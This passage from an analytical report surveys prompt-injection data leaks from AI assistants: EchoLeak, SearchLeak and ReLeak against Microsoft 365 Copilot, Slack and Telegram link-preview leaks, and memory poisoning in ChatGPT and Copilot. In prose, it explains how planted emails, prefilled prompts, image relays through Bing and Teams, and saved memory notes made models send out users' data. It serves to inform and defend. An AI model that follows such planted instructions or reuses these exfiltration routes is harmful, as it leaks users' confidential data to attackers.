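| May 2026 | OpenAI Codex | Fix without published details | PromptArmor |

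GitHub has not displayed any images in Copilot Chat since August 14, 2025, so the Camo method no longer works. Amazon had taken a similar step in January 2024, when it stopped its business assistant, Amazon Q, from producing links after a researcher showed that it could put a user's chat history into one.

OpenAI's optional Lockdown Mode turns off images in ChatGPT's answers, along with several other features, but the security website Anti-Abuse notes that OpenAI does not promise complete protection. A coding assistant probably needs images less than a general chatbot does, which may be why GitHub removed them for everyone and OpenAI did not.

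## Microsoft 365 Copilot: leaks through email, search links and saved files

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their company's email, files, calendars and chats. Between June 2025 and December 2026, security researchers published three sets of attacks on it, called EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak. All three extracted confidential data through convenience features, such as pictures in answers and documents that Copilot saved for the user. Microsoft has fixed the flaws, and neither the company nor the researchers have reported a real attack using them. Microsoft knew the basic method before EchoLeak, because it had fixed a leak through images in Bing Chat in 2023.

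### EchoLeak: an email that nobody opened

Suppose an employee asks Copilot how to apply for parental leave. The software first searches the employee's mailbox, Teams chats and stored files, along with the company's internal web pages, then gives the model the question and any passages that seem relevant. This method, called retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), saves the employee from finding the right document and pasting it in. But the software can retrieve emails the employee has never opened, so outsiders who can't use the company's Copilot can still get text into the model's input by emailing an employee.

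Aim Labs, Aim Security's research group, turned this into an attack. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, describes how the group made its email turn up in as many searches as possible. Such search software often cuts a long text into pieces and picks those closest in meaning to the question. Aim Labs therefore wrote a very long email that repeated the same instructions under many headings, including employee onboarding, common HR questions and leave of absence. A question about any of these topics could bring a piece of the email into Copilot's answer.

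Aim Labs had also considered a subtler method: changing a few characters in each copy of the text so that the search software would index the copies differently but the model could still read them. In a test with one of OpenAI's text-comparison models, where identical texts score 1, such changes lowered the similarity between a text and its altered copy to as little as 0.7. A phrase about greeting cards and another about the philosophy of science scored higher than that when compared with each other. But Aim Labs didn't know which comparison model Copilot used, so it couldn't tune the copies, and the plain headings worked well enough.

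Microsoft had a filter meant to stop injected instructions before they reached the model. Aim Labs got past it by writing the instructions as if they were for the email's recipient, without mentioning AI or Copilot. Even a much better filter would have trouble with this, because ordinary office email is full of requests to its reader.

The instructions told the reader to add the most sensitive information available to a web address, so the attacker didn't need to know what was in the victim's mailbox. To get the address out, Aim Labs first tried a link that the employee would have to click. Copilot removed links to outside websites from its answers, but only if the address came directly after the link's text, as it usually does in Markdown, the notation in which models write links and pictures. Microsoft's filter didn't recognize a lesser-known Markdown format that puts the address on a separate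 line, like a footnote.

The same format also worked for images. The browser loaded these automatically, as in the earlier attacks on ChatGPT and Bing Chat, so the group no longer needed a click.

The browser's Content Security Policy would still have blocked a picture from attacker.example. The policy's allow-list had about 30 entries, most of them for Microsoft's own services. Aim Labs searched these services for one that would fetch an outside address on request. It found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's service for internal websites, but the victim would have had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site. A Teams address could also fetch outside addresses, and it required no invitation. The browser could now request a picture from Teams, which the policy allowed, and a Teams server would forward the request to attacker.example with the stolen data.

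Willison (2025) calls the Teams address an open redirect, but by Ravia's account, Microsoft's server made the second request itself. The difference matters to designers because a Content Security Policy controls only what the browser loads, so it can't stop a server from contacting another server.

Copilot normally lists the documents behind an answer, which might have led the employee to the strange email. Aim Labs added a line to the email telling the recipient that, for compliance reasons, they should never refer to it, and Copilot left the email off the list.

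Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click vulnerability in a major AI application to cause concrete security damage without depending on specific user behavior. Ravia says earlier attacks either needed the user to send the chatbot to a malicious page or could extract only limited data. Willison describes EchoLeak as an extended version of an attack that researchers had already demonstrated in a dozen products. Both descriptions seem fair. The image trick was old, but in EchoLeak Copilot's own search retrieved the attacker's text, and the employee had no reason to suspect that an outside email was involved.

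Ravia and Willison also disagree about terminology. Ravia proposes "LLM scope violation" for cases in which untrusted text makes a model use private data from elsewhere in its context. Willison doesn't think this needs its own name, since language models have never been able to take account of where their text came from. The proposed term does point to a possible defense. In *EchoLeak*, Reddy and Gujral (2025) recommend access control based on provenance, in which the data available to the model depends on the origin of the text it's reading. The model would then have access to less data when reading an email from outside the company than when reading the employee's own question.

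Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025, and Microsoft had rolled out a fix by the time the attack became public on June 11. Microsoft said nobody had exploited the flaw in the wild, according to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*. CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, also recorded no exploitation but judged that attackers could automate the attack, according to the GCVE vulnerability database (2025). Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak a "real-world" exploit in the full title of their paper, which is accurate in the sense that it worked on a commercial product, though it had no known victims.

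Companies using Copilot could do little to protect themselves beforehand. Ravia knew of no administrator setting that would have prevented the attack. SOC Prime's *CVE-2025-32711 Vulnerability* describes two controls that Microsoft offered as further protection. One stops Copilot from processing outside email, and the other keeps it away from emails with sensitivity labels. Both can make Copilot less useful. Excluding outside email would remove one route for untrusted content, which is part of the lethal trifecta, but a salesperson might want Copilot mainly for messages from customers.

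### SearchLeak: a question already filled in

Search engines commonly put a user's query in the address of the results page so that people can save or share a search. Copilot's search page for businesses did this too, putting the query after the letter "q". A link to an ordinary search engine determines only what the recipient searches for, but Copilot passed the query to a language model as a prompt. A stranger who prepared such a link could therefore choose what the model did with the recipient's mail.

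*SearchLeak*, published by the data security company Varonis on June 15, 2026, describes an attack that needed only one click. The link opened the real Copilot search page, and the model immediately ran the prompt contained in the link. In the demonstration, the prompt told Copilot to find an email and put its subject line into an image's address. Many services put sign-in codes in the subject line, so an attacker might have time to use a code that had just arrived. Copilot could also search the victim's calendar, meeting notes and any company files the victim had permission to read.

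The link put the attacker's text where the employee's own question would normally go, so even a system that perfectly separated users' questions from retrieved documents would have treated it as coming from the employee. Keeping outside email away from Copilot wouldn't have helped either, because the link could arrive through any messaging app. Varonis advises users to inspect links before clicking, but this one led to a genuine Microsoft site, and most people can't tell what a long string of encoded text after "q" will do.

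Microsoft could have kept most of the convenience by putting the text in the search box and waiting for the employee to press a key. The employee could then have read the prompt first, though some people would surely have pressed the key without looking.

Varonis had used prefilled prompts before in Reprompt, an attack on the consumer version of Copilot. Varonis reported the attack to Microsoft in August 2025, and Microsoft patched it in January 2026, according to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*. Varonis was surprised that the technique still worked on the business version, which was supposed to have extra safeguards.

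One of those safeguards failed because of another convenience. Copilot displays an answer while the model is still writing it, so that users don't have to wait for the full text. Microsoft's filter turned image markup into harmless plain text, but only after the model had finished. By then, the browser had already treated the markup as a real image and sent a request for it. A tester who inspected only the finished answer would have concluded that the filter worked.

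The browser's allow-list still blocked attacker.example, so Varonis used Bing as a relay. When a user gives Bing's image search the address of a picture, a Bing server fetches the picture to analyze it. Copilot's policy allowed images from bing.com, so the browser sent its request to Bing, and Bing's server contacted attacker.example with the email title in the address.

Ravia had published the full allow-list, including bing.com, a year earlier. Tenable had also used bing.com addresses to get data out of ChatGPT, though by a different method. Varonis recommends looking for any allowed domain whose servers fetch addresses that users supply, and filtering an answer as the browser displays it rather than afterward.

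Microsoft published *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), its record of SearchLeak, on June 4, after fully repairing the flaw. It recorded no exploitation and told customers they didn't need to do anything. Microsoft rated the flaw critical but scored it 6.5 out of 10. The Next Web attributes that score to the click an attack required.

SearchLeak needed the prefilled prompt, the late filter and the Bing relay, so Microsoft could stop it by fixing any one of them. The record doesn't show which ones Microsoft fixed. Fixing only one would have stopped the reported attack but left the other weaknesses open to later attacks.

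### ReLeak: pictures, saved files and a sandbox

On December 3, 2026, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) announced three more zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. They came from the team that had found EchoLeak, now called Cato AI Labs because Cato Networks had bought Aim Security. As in EchoLeak, the attacker sent an email that the employee never opened, and Copilot retrieved it while answering an ordinary work question. The attacks differed in how the data left.

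ReLeak also leaked data through an image's address. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, explains that Copilot put confidential information into the address, the browser loaded the image, and Bing fetched it from the attacker's server. The attack combined EchoLeak's unopened email with SearchLeak's relay. It needed no clicks, whereas SearchLeak had needed at least one, as Antipov (2026) points out in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* ("You don't even have to open the email").

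Microsoft had declared SearchLeak fully repaired on June 4. Cato reported its findings between July 29 and August 20, so Bing was passing on stolen data again within three months. The public accounts don't show whether Microsoft left the relay alone in June and repaired another part of SearchLeak, or whether Cato found a new way to reach it.

Another attack used Copilot's ability to create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files and save them in OneDrive or SharePoint. The hidden instructions made Copilot save a document with a link that contained confidential data. Microsoft's servers process stored files in the background, and in Cato's tests this processing sent the data out one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, without anyone having to open the document.

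Closing the chat therefore didn't protect the employee. A filter that checked Copilot's answer for suspicious links could miss this attack, because the link was in a file. The browser's allow-list didn't apply, because the request came from Microsoft's file-processing system. A designer who assumes a task ends when the document is saved can easily overlook what other software will do with it later.

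Cato also got data out of the isolated sandbox where Copilot runs short programs, although Microsoft promised in its documentation that the sandbox had no incoming or outgoing network traffic. Customers can give the same programming tool to agents they build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio, but Antipov reports no confirmation that the flaw affected those agents.

Cato's researchers used AI agents to write test cases, analyze why Copilot had refused a request and adjust the next attempt. An attacker could do the same, so a filter that stops the first few versions of an attack may soon fail against a system that keeps rewording it.

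Microsoft repaired the sandbox on September 17, four to seven weeks after Cato's reports. The file attack worked until November 11 and the image attack until November 15, at least twelve weeks after Cato reported it. It seems odd that the image attack, the most familiar route, took the longest to close. Bing's image fetching is part of a public search engine, so Microsoft may have found it hard to restrict without breaking something else, but the company hasn't explained the delay. Microsoft made all the repairs on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install.

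The table lists each flaw's number in CVE, the public catalog of software vulnerabilities. When Cato published ReLeak, two of its three numbers were only reserved, without full public records. The sandbox flaw's score was initially 7.4. Microsoft's score for EchoLeak is 9.3, higher than the 7.5 in the US National Vulnerability Database, mainly because Microsoft assumed that the damage could reach beyond Copilot.

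| Attack | CVE number | Severity score out of 10 | Reported to Microsoft | Repaired | Source |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | CVE-2025-32711 | 9.3 | January 2025 | By June 11, 2025 | GCVE; Willison |
| SearchLeak | CVE-2026-42824 | 6.5 | Date not given | By June 4, 2026 | Microsoft |
| ReLeak, images | CVE-2026-124115 | Not confirmed | July 29 to August 20, 2026 | November 15, 2026 | Faisal |
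| ReLeak, saved files | CVE-2026-124132 | Not confirmed | July 29 to August 20, 2026 | November 11, 2026 | Faisal |
| ReLeak, sandbox | CVE-2026-78501 | 8.6 | July 29 to August 20, 2026 | September 17, 2026 | Faisal |

Microsoft's assistants had other leaks besides the flaw in Copilot Cowork. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot* describes CoSnitch, a Copilot attack that Varonis disclosed in August 2026. Microsoft's records for 2026 also include at least one other information leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot, *CVE-2026-26129 M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026).

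### Microsoft's layers of defense

Microsoft (2025) described its defenses in July 2025, a month after EchoLeak became public. It tries to prevent injections by strengthening the model's standing instructions and by marking off untrusted text with a technique called Spotlighting. It tries to detect them with a scanner called Prompt Shields. To limit the damage from any that get through, it restricts access to data, asks users for consent to some actions and uses fixed rules to block known methods of exfiltration. It also funds research into safer designs.

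Microsoft advises developers to assume that indirect prompt injection is inevitable and to design systems that contain it. The attacks on Copilot support this advice. In 2025, Aim Labs got past the injection filter with an email written like normal correspondence, and in 2026 Microsoft's protections failed to stop any of the three ReLeak attacks. Marking text as untrusted may not help enough either, since Ye and colleagues found that models often rely more on a text's style than on its label.

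If injections will sometimes succeed, the fixed rules that block exfiltration matter most. A persuasive email can't change which addresses a fixed rule blocks, but these rules cover only the methods their designers thought of. Microsoft had a rule for links and images, but Aim Labs got around it by using a different format. Microsoft also had a rule for image markup, but Varonis's image loaded before the rule took effect. The rules for what a browser may load didn't apply to the file that Copilot saved.

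The consent steps didn't help because these attacks didn't trigger any of them. Microsoft had reason not to ask for consent, since few users would want to approve every picture or saved document, and loading a picture from Microsoft's own servers looks harmless until someone finds that the server will forward the request.

Faisal quotes Cato as saying that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Cato sells security products for AI systems, and Ravia's article on EchoLeak also promotes the company's protective software, so both have a commercial interest in a gloomy assessment. Still, Cato demonstrated in 2025 that an unopened email could make Copilot leak data, and did so again in 2026 despite Microsoft's repairs.

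Faisal attributes the repeated leaks to Copilot's growing abilities, each of which gave data a new way out. This fits the leaks through saved files and the sandbox, but not those through pictures, because Copilot already displayed pictures when Aim Labs attacked it in 2025, and bing.com was already on the allow-list. Microsoft was adding new ways out faster than it closed the old ones, and it had also left at least one old one usable after two public warnings.

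In all these attacks, one of Microsoft's servers sent the request to the attacker's server. A company that monitored its employees' computers would have seen them connect only to Microsoft, so customers would have had little chance of noticing a theft themselves. That also makes it hard for them to check statements about whether anyone exploited the flaws. Microsoft stated that nobody had exploited EchoLeak or SearchLeak, and it could at least examine its own servers. For ReLeak, the public assurance comes from Cato, which knew of no affected customers but had no view of most customers' systems.

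Microsoft could fix the picture leaks more broadly by adopting OpenAI's current rule for ChatGPT, which automatically loads only addresses already found on the public web. Under that rule, Copilot would have refused to load the long Teams and Bing addresses, even though Microsoft owned both domains, because each address contained data from a private conversation. For saved files, Microsoft would have to apply the rule in its file-processing system as well as in the chat window.

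## Link previews in Slack, Telegram and Teams

When someone posts a link in Slack, Telegram or Microsoft Teams, the app usually shows a preview under the message with the page's title, a short description and often a picture. To make the preview, the app has to request the page. If the link contains private data, as in the picture attacks on chat products, the page's owner receives that data with the request. Messaging apps had previews long before AI assistants, and their designers could assume that a person had written the link.

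### Which computer requests the page

Security Intelligence distinguishes three ways to make a link preview. In the first, the sender's app makes the preview and sends it with the message, as iMessage and WhatsApp do according to MacRumors' *Link Previews in Popular Messaging Apps May Lead to Security Vulnerabilities* (2020). In the second, an outside server makes it, as it did for Slack, LinkedIn and Zoom when TechBeacon's *Messenger apps* listed them. In the third, the recipient's app requests the page when the message arrives.

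The security researchers Talal Haj Bakry and Tommy Mysk examined these methods. Mysk's *Link Previews* (2020) reports that some apps revealed users' internet addresses, exposed links from encrypted chats or quietly downloaded gigabytes of data. The main worry then was that a malicious page could harm the person who received the link. A preview made by the sender's app avoids that, because the recipient's device doesn't contact the page until the recipient opens the link.

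When a model writes a link, the address itself can contain confidential data. None of the three methods prevents the leak, because some computer still requests the full address. A person would have to copy a confidential message into an address before a preview could leak it, but Slack points out in its security guide for developers that a model can find the data, format it and post it without the user's consent.

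A link preview can send data to an attacker just as a click would. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* explains that both send the same type of request. If Slack's server sends it, the attacker doesn't learn the user's IP address but still gets everything the model put after the question mark in the URL.

Rehberger noticed this in 2023 after building a chatbot for Discord, a group-chat app. Embrace The Red's *Don't blindly trust LLM responses. Threats to chatbots* includes server logs from that April with automatic requests from Discord, Skype, Slack, Telegram, Signal and Teams. Signal sent six requests, for addresses ending in /s, /si, /sig and so on up to /signal, apparently because it was looking up the link while Rehberger was still typing it.

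### Slack AI: a leak that needed a click

Slack AI answers employees' questions using messages from the private channels they belong to and all the company's public channels, including those they have never joined. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, published in August 2024, describes how someone with an account in the same Slack workspace could use this to get another person's secrets.

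In the demonstration, a developer had saved an API key (a code that lets a program use an online service) in a private channel with no other members. The attacker created a public channel, also with no other members, and posted an instruction there. When the developer asked Slack AI for the key, the search found both messages. Slack AI answered with what looked like an error message and a link to sign in again. The key was in the link's address, so clicking the link sent the key to the attacker.

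The developer had little chance of tracing the answer to the attacker, because Slack AI cited only the private channel as its source and the attacker's message wasn't on the first page of search results. In another test, PromptArmor made Slack AI add a phishing link to an answer about a colleague's messages. Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel that time, so users couldn't rely on citations to reveal an attack.

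PromptArmor reported the flaw on August 14, the same day Slack AI began reading uploaded files. That change may have let an attacker without an account give Slack AI instructions through a document that an employee uploaded. PromptArmor considered this highly likely but had finished testing before the change.

Slack replied on August 19 that the evidence was insufficient. It said the information in PromptArmor's first video came from a public channel, and that letting every member search public channels was "intended behavior". This didn't address the attack PromptArmor published, in which the key was in a private channel and only the instruction was in a public one. Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, took the reply as a sign that Slack didn't yet understand the problem. Salesforce, which owns Slack, later told Candid.Technology that it had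 deployed a patch and had no evidence of unauthorized access to customer data.

The same month, Rehberger warned in Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* that an app's messages could leak data without a click. "Unfurling" is Slack's word for making a link preview. In his example, a chatbot posts a link containing part of the earlier conversation, and Slack leaks that text when it requests the link for the preview. Rehberger adds that an attacker could encode the data in invisible characters, so the link would look ordinary to the user.

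Few developers seem to have considered this vulnerability in 2024. Willison (2024) had been writing about prompt injection for almost two years, but said he "hadn't thought about" it before.

### Anthropic's Slack connector

When Anthropic introduced MCP, it published sample connectors for developers to use or copy. The one for Slack didn't turn off link previews when it posted a message. Rehberger reported this to Anthropic on May 27, 2025, and described two demonstrations in Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory*.

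In one case, a developer asked Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to analyze a source file that contained invisible instructions. The agent read an API key from another file on the developer's computer and posted a link containing the key to Slack. Slack then requested the link several times. In the other case, a user asked the Claude desktop app to summarize a document for colleagues. The document made Claude copy the latest message from one Slack channel into a link and post the link in a private channel.

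An administrator could restrict the connector to posting in a single private channel. Since only colleagues can read that channel, the administrator might reasonably let the agent post without the user approval that most AI products request before running a tool. Link previews defeat the restriction because Slack sends the link's address to an outside server, even though the message stays in the channel.

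Anthropic archived the connector two days after the report. Rehberger doesn't know whether the report prompted this. Anthropic had no plans to repair connectors it no longer maintained, and it agreed to publication. The package still had more than 14,000 downloads a week. Rehberger estimated there could be tens of thousands of vulnerable installations, though repeated downloads may inflate that number. He demonstrated the leak on his own accounts and reports no theft by anyone else.

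The flaw was published as CVE-2025-34072 on July 2, 2025. VulnCheck's *Anthropic Slack MCP Server Data Exfiltration via Link Unfurling* rates it 9.3 out of 10 and lists all default installations as affected, while Rehberger scored it 7.5. VulnCheck's rating assumes that the attacker needs no account and the victim does nothing. Those assumptions fit an agent that posts unsupervised, but the rating seems high for a user who reads every message before approving it. Snyk's *Improper Neutralization of Input Used for LLM Prompting* (2025) states that no fixed version exists, so anyone still using the connector has to change its code, which Rehberger's fix does in two lines.

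### PromptArmor's tests of agents in messaging apps

By early 2026, many people were giving instructions to AI agents through the messaging apps they already used. One agent was OpenClaw, which people run on their own computers and can message through Telegram. In February, PromptArmor opened a public website where users could test their own combinations of agent and app.

The user had the agent post a link to the test site. If the messaging app requested the link, the site recorded the request, the program that sent it and any data in the address. The user could then report which agent had written the message. Users could also report combinations of agent and app that produced no request, and PromptArmor displayed both kinds of result.

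OpenClaw on Telegram leaked data to a test site with its default settings. The site received no more data after the user turned off Telegram previews in OpenClaw's settings. In *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, Apostol also lists Slack, Discord, and Teams with agents made in Microsoft's Copilot Studio among the affected systems.

Volunteers chose what to test, so these results can't show how common the problem is. A combination reported as safe may become unsafe if someone changes a setting. The site tested whether a preview would send data out, not whether an attacker could get the agent to write the link. PromptArmor doesn't report any thefts.

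In August 2026, OpenClaw's Telegram documentation still listed link previews as on by default. OpenClaw is much more careful about who can give the agent orders. The owner must approve strangers before the agent accepts their private messages, and the agent ignores groups the owner hasn't listed. But these rules don't stop instructions hidden in a web page that the agent reads while working for its owner.

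### Turning previews off

Slack lets an app turn off the preview for each message it posts. Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* describes two settings, one for text pages and one for images, video and audio. Slack's servers have to request an address to find out which kind of content it leads to, so a developer who turns off only one setting may stop the card from appearing without stopping the request. Slack says it won't request the page if both are off. A missing card doesn't prove that there was no request, so a developer should check the linked server's logs.

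By default, Slack generates link previews for messages from apps as well as people. Rehberger thinks any AI system that posts to a messaging app should have previews off unless someone deliberately turns them on, and Slack now recommends the same to developers of AI apps. Losing previews matters little for an assistant that posts meeting summaries, but more for one that shares news articles, because readers may use the previews to decide what to open.

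Developers who want to keep some previews can check the links a model writes against an allow-list of domains, as Slack and Rehberger suggest. Like the allow-lists for pictures, such a list can fail if it includes a site that forwards requests or accepts data from anyone. OpenAI mentions link previews, along with embedded images, as background requests that a user may never notice. But another company's server makes the request for a preview, so OpenAI's rule of automatically loading only publicly known addresses would have to cover the links an agent writes as well as the pages it loads.

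Slack also suggests telling the model never to put private data in a web address, but acknowledges that such instructions aren't a complete solution.

Even without a preview, someone may click on the harmful link in the message, as in the Slack AI attack. Only checking or removing the link protects a user who would click on it.

### When one company makes the agent and another the preview

In the OpenClaw case, Telegram supplies the preview and OpenClaw decides whether to ask for one. Telegram can't easily tell that an address contains someone's password, and OpenClaw doesn't control Telegram's servers, so each can regard its own part as working normally. PromptArmor thinks messaging companies should offer preview settings and agent developers should use them or let users choose. It would also like messaging apps to let people turn off previews for a whole channel, which would protect users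 even when a developer forgets the setting.

Slack disputed the 2024 report, but its security guide now describes the preview attack step by step. Slack still leaves the fix to developers. The guide says "the app" sends the request to the attacker's site, while Slack's page on previews says Slack's own servers request the links in a message. An app can take over previews for web domains it has registered, but an attacker's domain wouldn't normally be among them. A developer who followed the guide and restricted only the app's own connections could therefore fail to block the request from Slack's servers.

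Slack could turn previews off by default for every app, but this would remove them from many ordinary apps that rely on them. It could instead ask developers to declare which apps post text written by a model, but this would depend on developers doing so honestly and carefully. Still, one change at Slack would protect users of connectors that nobody maintains, such as Anthropic's. PromptArmor's article on the 2026 tests includes no replies from Slack, Telegram, Discord or Microsoft.

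An AI agent and a chat app aren't necessarily safer together because the same company makes them. Microsoft makes both Copilot Cowork and Teams, but PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* shows that Cowork could send its user emails and Teams messages without approval, even though Microsoft said in its documentation that Cowork would ask first.

PromptArmor hid instructions in a skill, a file that describes how the Cowork agent should do a task. Cowork then sent its user a Teams message with external images, whose addresses contained file download links that anyone could use. When the user opened the message, Teams requested the images. This sent the links to the attacker, who could then download the files. All five attempts succeeded.

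Users can't make Cowork ask for approval in this case. PromptArmor treats the problem as a risk of the product's design, not a specific bug, and reports no fix. Administrators can limit the damage by blocking downloads of sensitive files, but employees then can't print those files or open them in Word or Excel.

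## Memory in ChatGPT and Copilot

A leak through a picture or a link preview usually ends with the conversation in which the model read the attacker's text, but memory can make it last much longer. ChatGPT and Copilot save notes about their users for later conversations, so people don't have to explain their job or diet each time. Security researchers have repeatedly used web pages and files to add such notes, and some companies have tried to do the same to promote their products.

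### How a note gets into memory and comes back

ChatGPT's memory began in April 2024 as a list of saved facts. According to OpenAI's *Dreaming*, the model added to the list during a conversation, usually after a strong cue such as a request to remember a trip to Singapore. A year later, OpenAI added a background process called dreaming, which reviews past chats and keeps what seems useful without an explicit request. A more capable version followed in mid-2026.

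ChatGPT stores saved memories separately from chats, so deleting a chat doesn't delete the memories saved from it. According to OpenAI's help page *Memory in ChatGPT*, memory can also draw on a user's stored files and connected apps such as Gmail, depending on the plan and region.

The model retains nothing between conversations, so the product has to give it the notes each time. *PersistBench* (2026), a test of how models use memories, describes the simplest arrangement, in which the software puts every note alongside the product's standing instructions, before the user's new question. Other products search the notes and add only those that seem relevant.

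A single prompt injection can therefore keep working for months. *MemoryDojo* (Yang, Bullwinkel et al., 2026) gives the example of an email that falsely says the user prefers to have invoices forwarded to a certain address. An assistant without memory might leak one invoice, but one that saves the preference might also forward every later invoice, long after the email has dropped out of the conversation.

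Saving the text also hides where it came from. *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (Dash, Ge and colleagues, 2026) found no robust mechanism in current systems for tracking the origin of stored notes. The assistant can therefore later treat a stranger's sentence as a fact about its user. Defenses that treat emails and web pages as untrusted may no longer apply to that sentence.

### From custom instructions to SpAIware

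In 2023, before ChatGPT had a memory, OpenAI let users write custom instructions that applied to every exchange. Embrace the Red's *ChatGPT Custom Instructions* shows how these could make the image leak permanent. Rehberger entered an instruction to end each answer with an image whose address contained a summary of the user's message and ChatGPT's reply. He compared this to the email forwarding rules that intruders set up in a mailbox. An attacker would presumably have needed to get access to the account first or persuade the user to paste in the text.

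Memory removed that obstacle because ChatGPT could write to it while reading a stranger's web page. In May 2024, Rehberger reported to OpenAI that a website could plant false memories, and OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue. In June, he sent a demonstration that also used the planted memory to steal data.

Embrace the Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*, published that September, describes the attack on ChatGPT's macOS app. The user asked ChatGPT to look at a web page containing the attacker's instructions. ChatGPT followed them and saved a memory containing an instruction to leak every exchange through an invisible image. The memory carried over when the user started a new chat about something else, so the attacker still received everything the user typed and everything ChatGPT replied.

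OpenAI's url_safe check should have stopped the image from loading. But each app had to run the check itself, and OpenAI released its macOS and Android apps without it, even though Rehberger had already pointed out that the iPhone app lacked it.

In September 2024, OpenAI released version 1.2024.247 of the macOS app, which stopped it from sending conversations out through images. A website or document could still make ChatGPT save any memory. A planted memory could still make ChatGPT give false or slanted answers, and could leak data again if someone found another exfiltration channel. Rehberger reported no real victims and advised users to check their saved memories regularly.

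### ZombieAgent and the controls on ChatGPT's memory

By the time the security company Radware tested ChatGPT in 2025, OpenAI had added two restrictions. After using a connector such as Gmail, ChatGPT could not use its memory in the same chat, which kept an email from planting a note there. ChatGPT also could not open an attacker's web addresses stored in its memory, so a planted note could not make it send data out directly.

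Radware's *ZombieAgent*, published in January 2026, describes a way around both. The restriction on connectors worked in only one direction, so ChatGPT could still read its memory and then use Gmail. A file the user shared with ChatGPT could also still change the memory.

Radware's file planted two instructions in ChatGPT's memory. The first was to look for an email from the attacker with a particular subject line, and do what the email instructed, whenever the user sent a message. The second was to save any sensitive information the user mentioned. The email contained the web addresses for sending out data, so the ban on opening addresses from memory didn't apply. ChatGPT sent the stolen text one character at a time by opening a ready-made address for each character, much as Tenable had done with Bing links. The requests came from OpenAI's servers, so protections in the user's browser couldn't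 block them.

This design would presumably also let the attacker change the instructions by sending another email, without planting a new note. In a separate demonstration, Radware altered a user's stored medical history, and ChatGPT gave misleading health advice, a kind of harm that doesn't require any data to leave the account.

Radware reported the flaws on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed them on December 16. Radware does not describe the fix or report any thefts.

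Users can now read a summary of ChatGPT's memory, correct or delete notes, and sometimes see which memory, file or email influenced an answer. Temporary chats never create memories. However, OpenAI acknowledges that the summary can omit things and that the list of sources may be incomplete. Its help page mentions no rule against saving memories from web pages or files. It also doesn't explain how the old separation between connectors and memory works now that memory can draw on Gmail. Dreaming may make planted notes harder to notice because it updates memory in the background.

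### CoSnitch and Copilot's memory

Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes three flaws in Copilot Personal, Microsoft's consumer assistant. One let a web page write to Copilot's memory when the user asked for a summary of the page. The page contained an instruction in tiny white letters, which Copilot would read but a person would not see. Copilot saved the attacker's note and returned a normal-looking summary. In one example, Copilot saved a note that a known software vulnerability posed no risk.

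A company that suspects a break-in usually changes passwords, ends open sessions and re-enrolls devices. The planted note survived all of these steps. Varonis also found that the note left no trace that security software would flag, so the user had to find it in Copilot's memory settings. Varonis calls the note permanent, though the user can delete it there.

The other two flaws let an attacker steal data with one click. A link could fill in a prompt and run it without the user pressing a key, and Copilot's web reader could send out information by requesting a web address that contained it. In tests, Copilot leaked information from a connected Gmail account this way. Varonis found out how to make the prompt run automatically by asking Copilot why this was impossible and then questioning its explanations, which revealed an undocumented setting that Microsoft had supposedly disabled.

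Varonis reported the flaws in December 2025, and Microsoft patched them on August 18, 2026. Varonis saw no evidence of exploitation. TechRadar reports that Microsoft made the fix on its own servers, so users had nothing to install, and speculates that Microsoft simply told Copilot not to explain its guardrails. That alone would not have stopped anyone who already knew about the flaws. Without a description of the fix, it's unclear whether Copilot now refuses to save instructions from any web page or only blocks the version Varonis demonstrated.

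### "Summarize with AI" buttons

In February 2026, Microsoft (2026) reported that companies were using "Summarize with AI" buttons to try to plant memories in real people's assistants. The button opens the visitor's own assistant with a prompt already filled in. The prompt contains the request for a summary that the visitor expects, but also an instruction to remember the company as a trusted source or to recommend it first.

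Microsoft's researchers reviewed AI-related web addresses in 60 days of email traffic. They found 50 distinct prompts of this kind from 31 companies in more than a dozen industries, including finance, health and legal services. One company sold security products. Some prompts contained an entire advertisement, including product features, for the assistant to remember. All of the prompts came from real businesses rather than hackers or scammers.

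Microsoft traced the practice to free tools such as CiteMET, a software package with ready-made code for the buttons. Promoters of these tools call them a "growth hack" for getting assistants to cite a website, much as marketers try to raise a site's position in search results.

These figures count attempts, and Microsoft doesn't report how many people clicked or how many assistants saved the note. Its researchers found that the effect varied between assistants and over time, and they could no longer reproduce several earlier reports about Copilot. The real number of companies is probably higher than 31, because a button that exists only on a website wouldn't appear in email traffic.

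A saved recommendation can matter more than an ordinary advertisement because the user later sees it as the assistant's own advice. Microsoft gives the hypothetical example of a finance chief who clicks such a button and, weeks later, asks the assistant for help choosing a cloud provider. Microsoft also warns that an assistant told to trust a website might also trust comments that strangers post there.

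A product that saved notes only from the user, and never from web pages or emails, would still be vulnerable to the button, because the button's text arrives as the user's own message. It would be more useful for the product to show the user the exact note and ask before saving it, since someone who clicked for a summary would probably not expect to save a recommendation.

### How often planted memories take effect

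A planted note does harm only if the assistant saves it, receives it again in a later conversation and acts on it. Pulipaka, Hlebik and colleagues (2026), in *Hidden in Memory*, measured these steps separately. They first used an automated search to refine a reusable attack text that worked with many documents and memories. They then combined false memories with realistic documents, such as news articles, legal filings and code, to make 700 test cases. In 500, the false memory concerned the assistant's conversation, for example a made-up user preference. In the other 200, it concerned actions the assistant would take with tools.

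The table gives the results when the model itself decided what to save. The last two columns cover later tasks on a related subject, after the planted note had been retrieved from memory.

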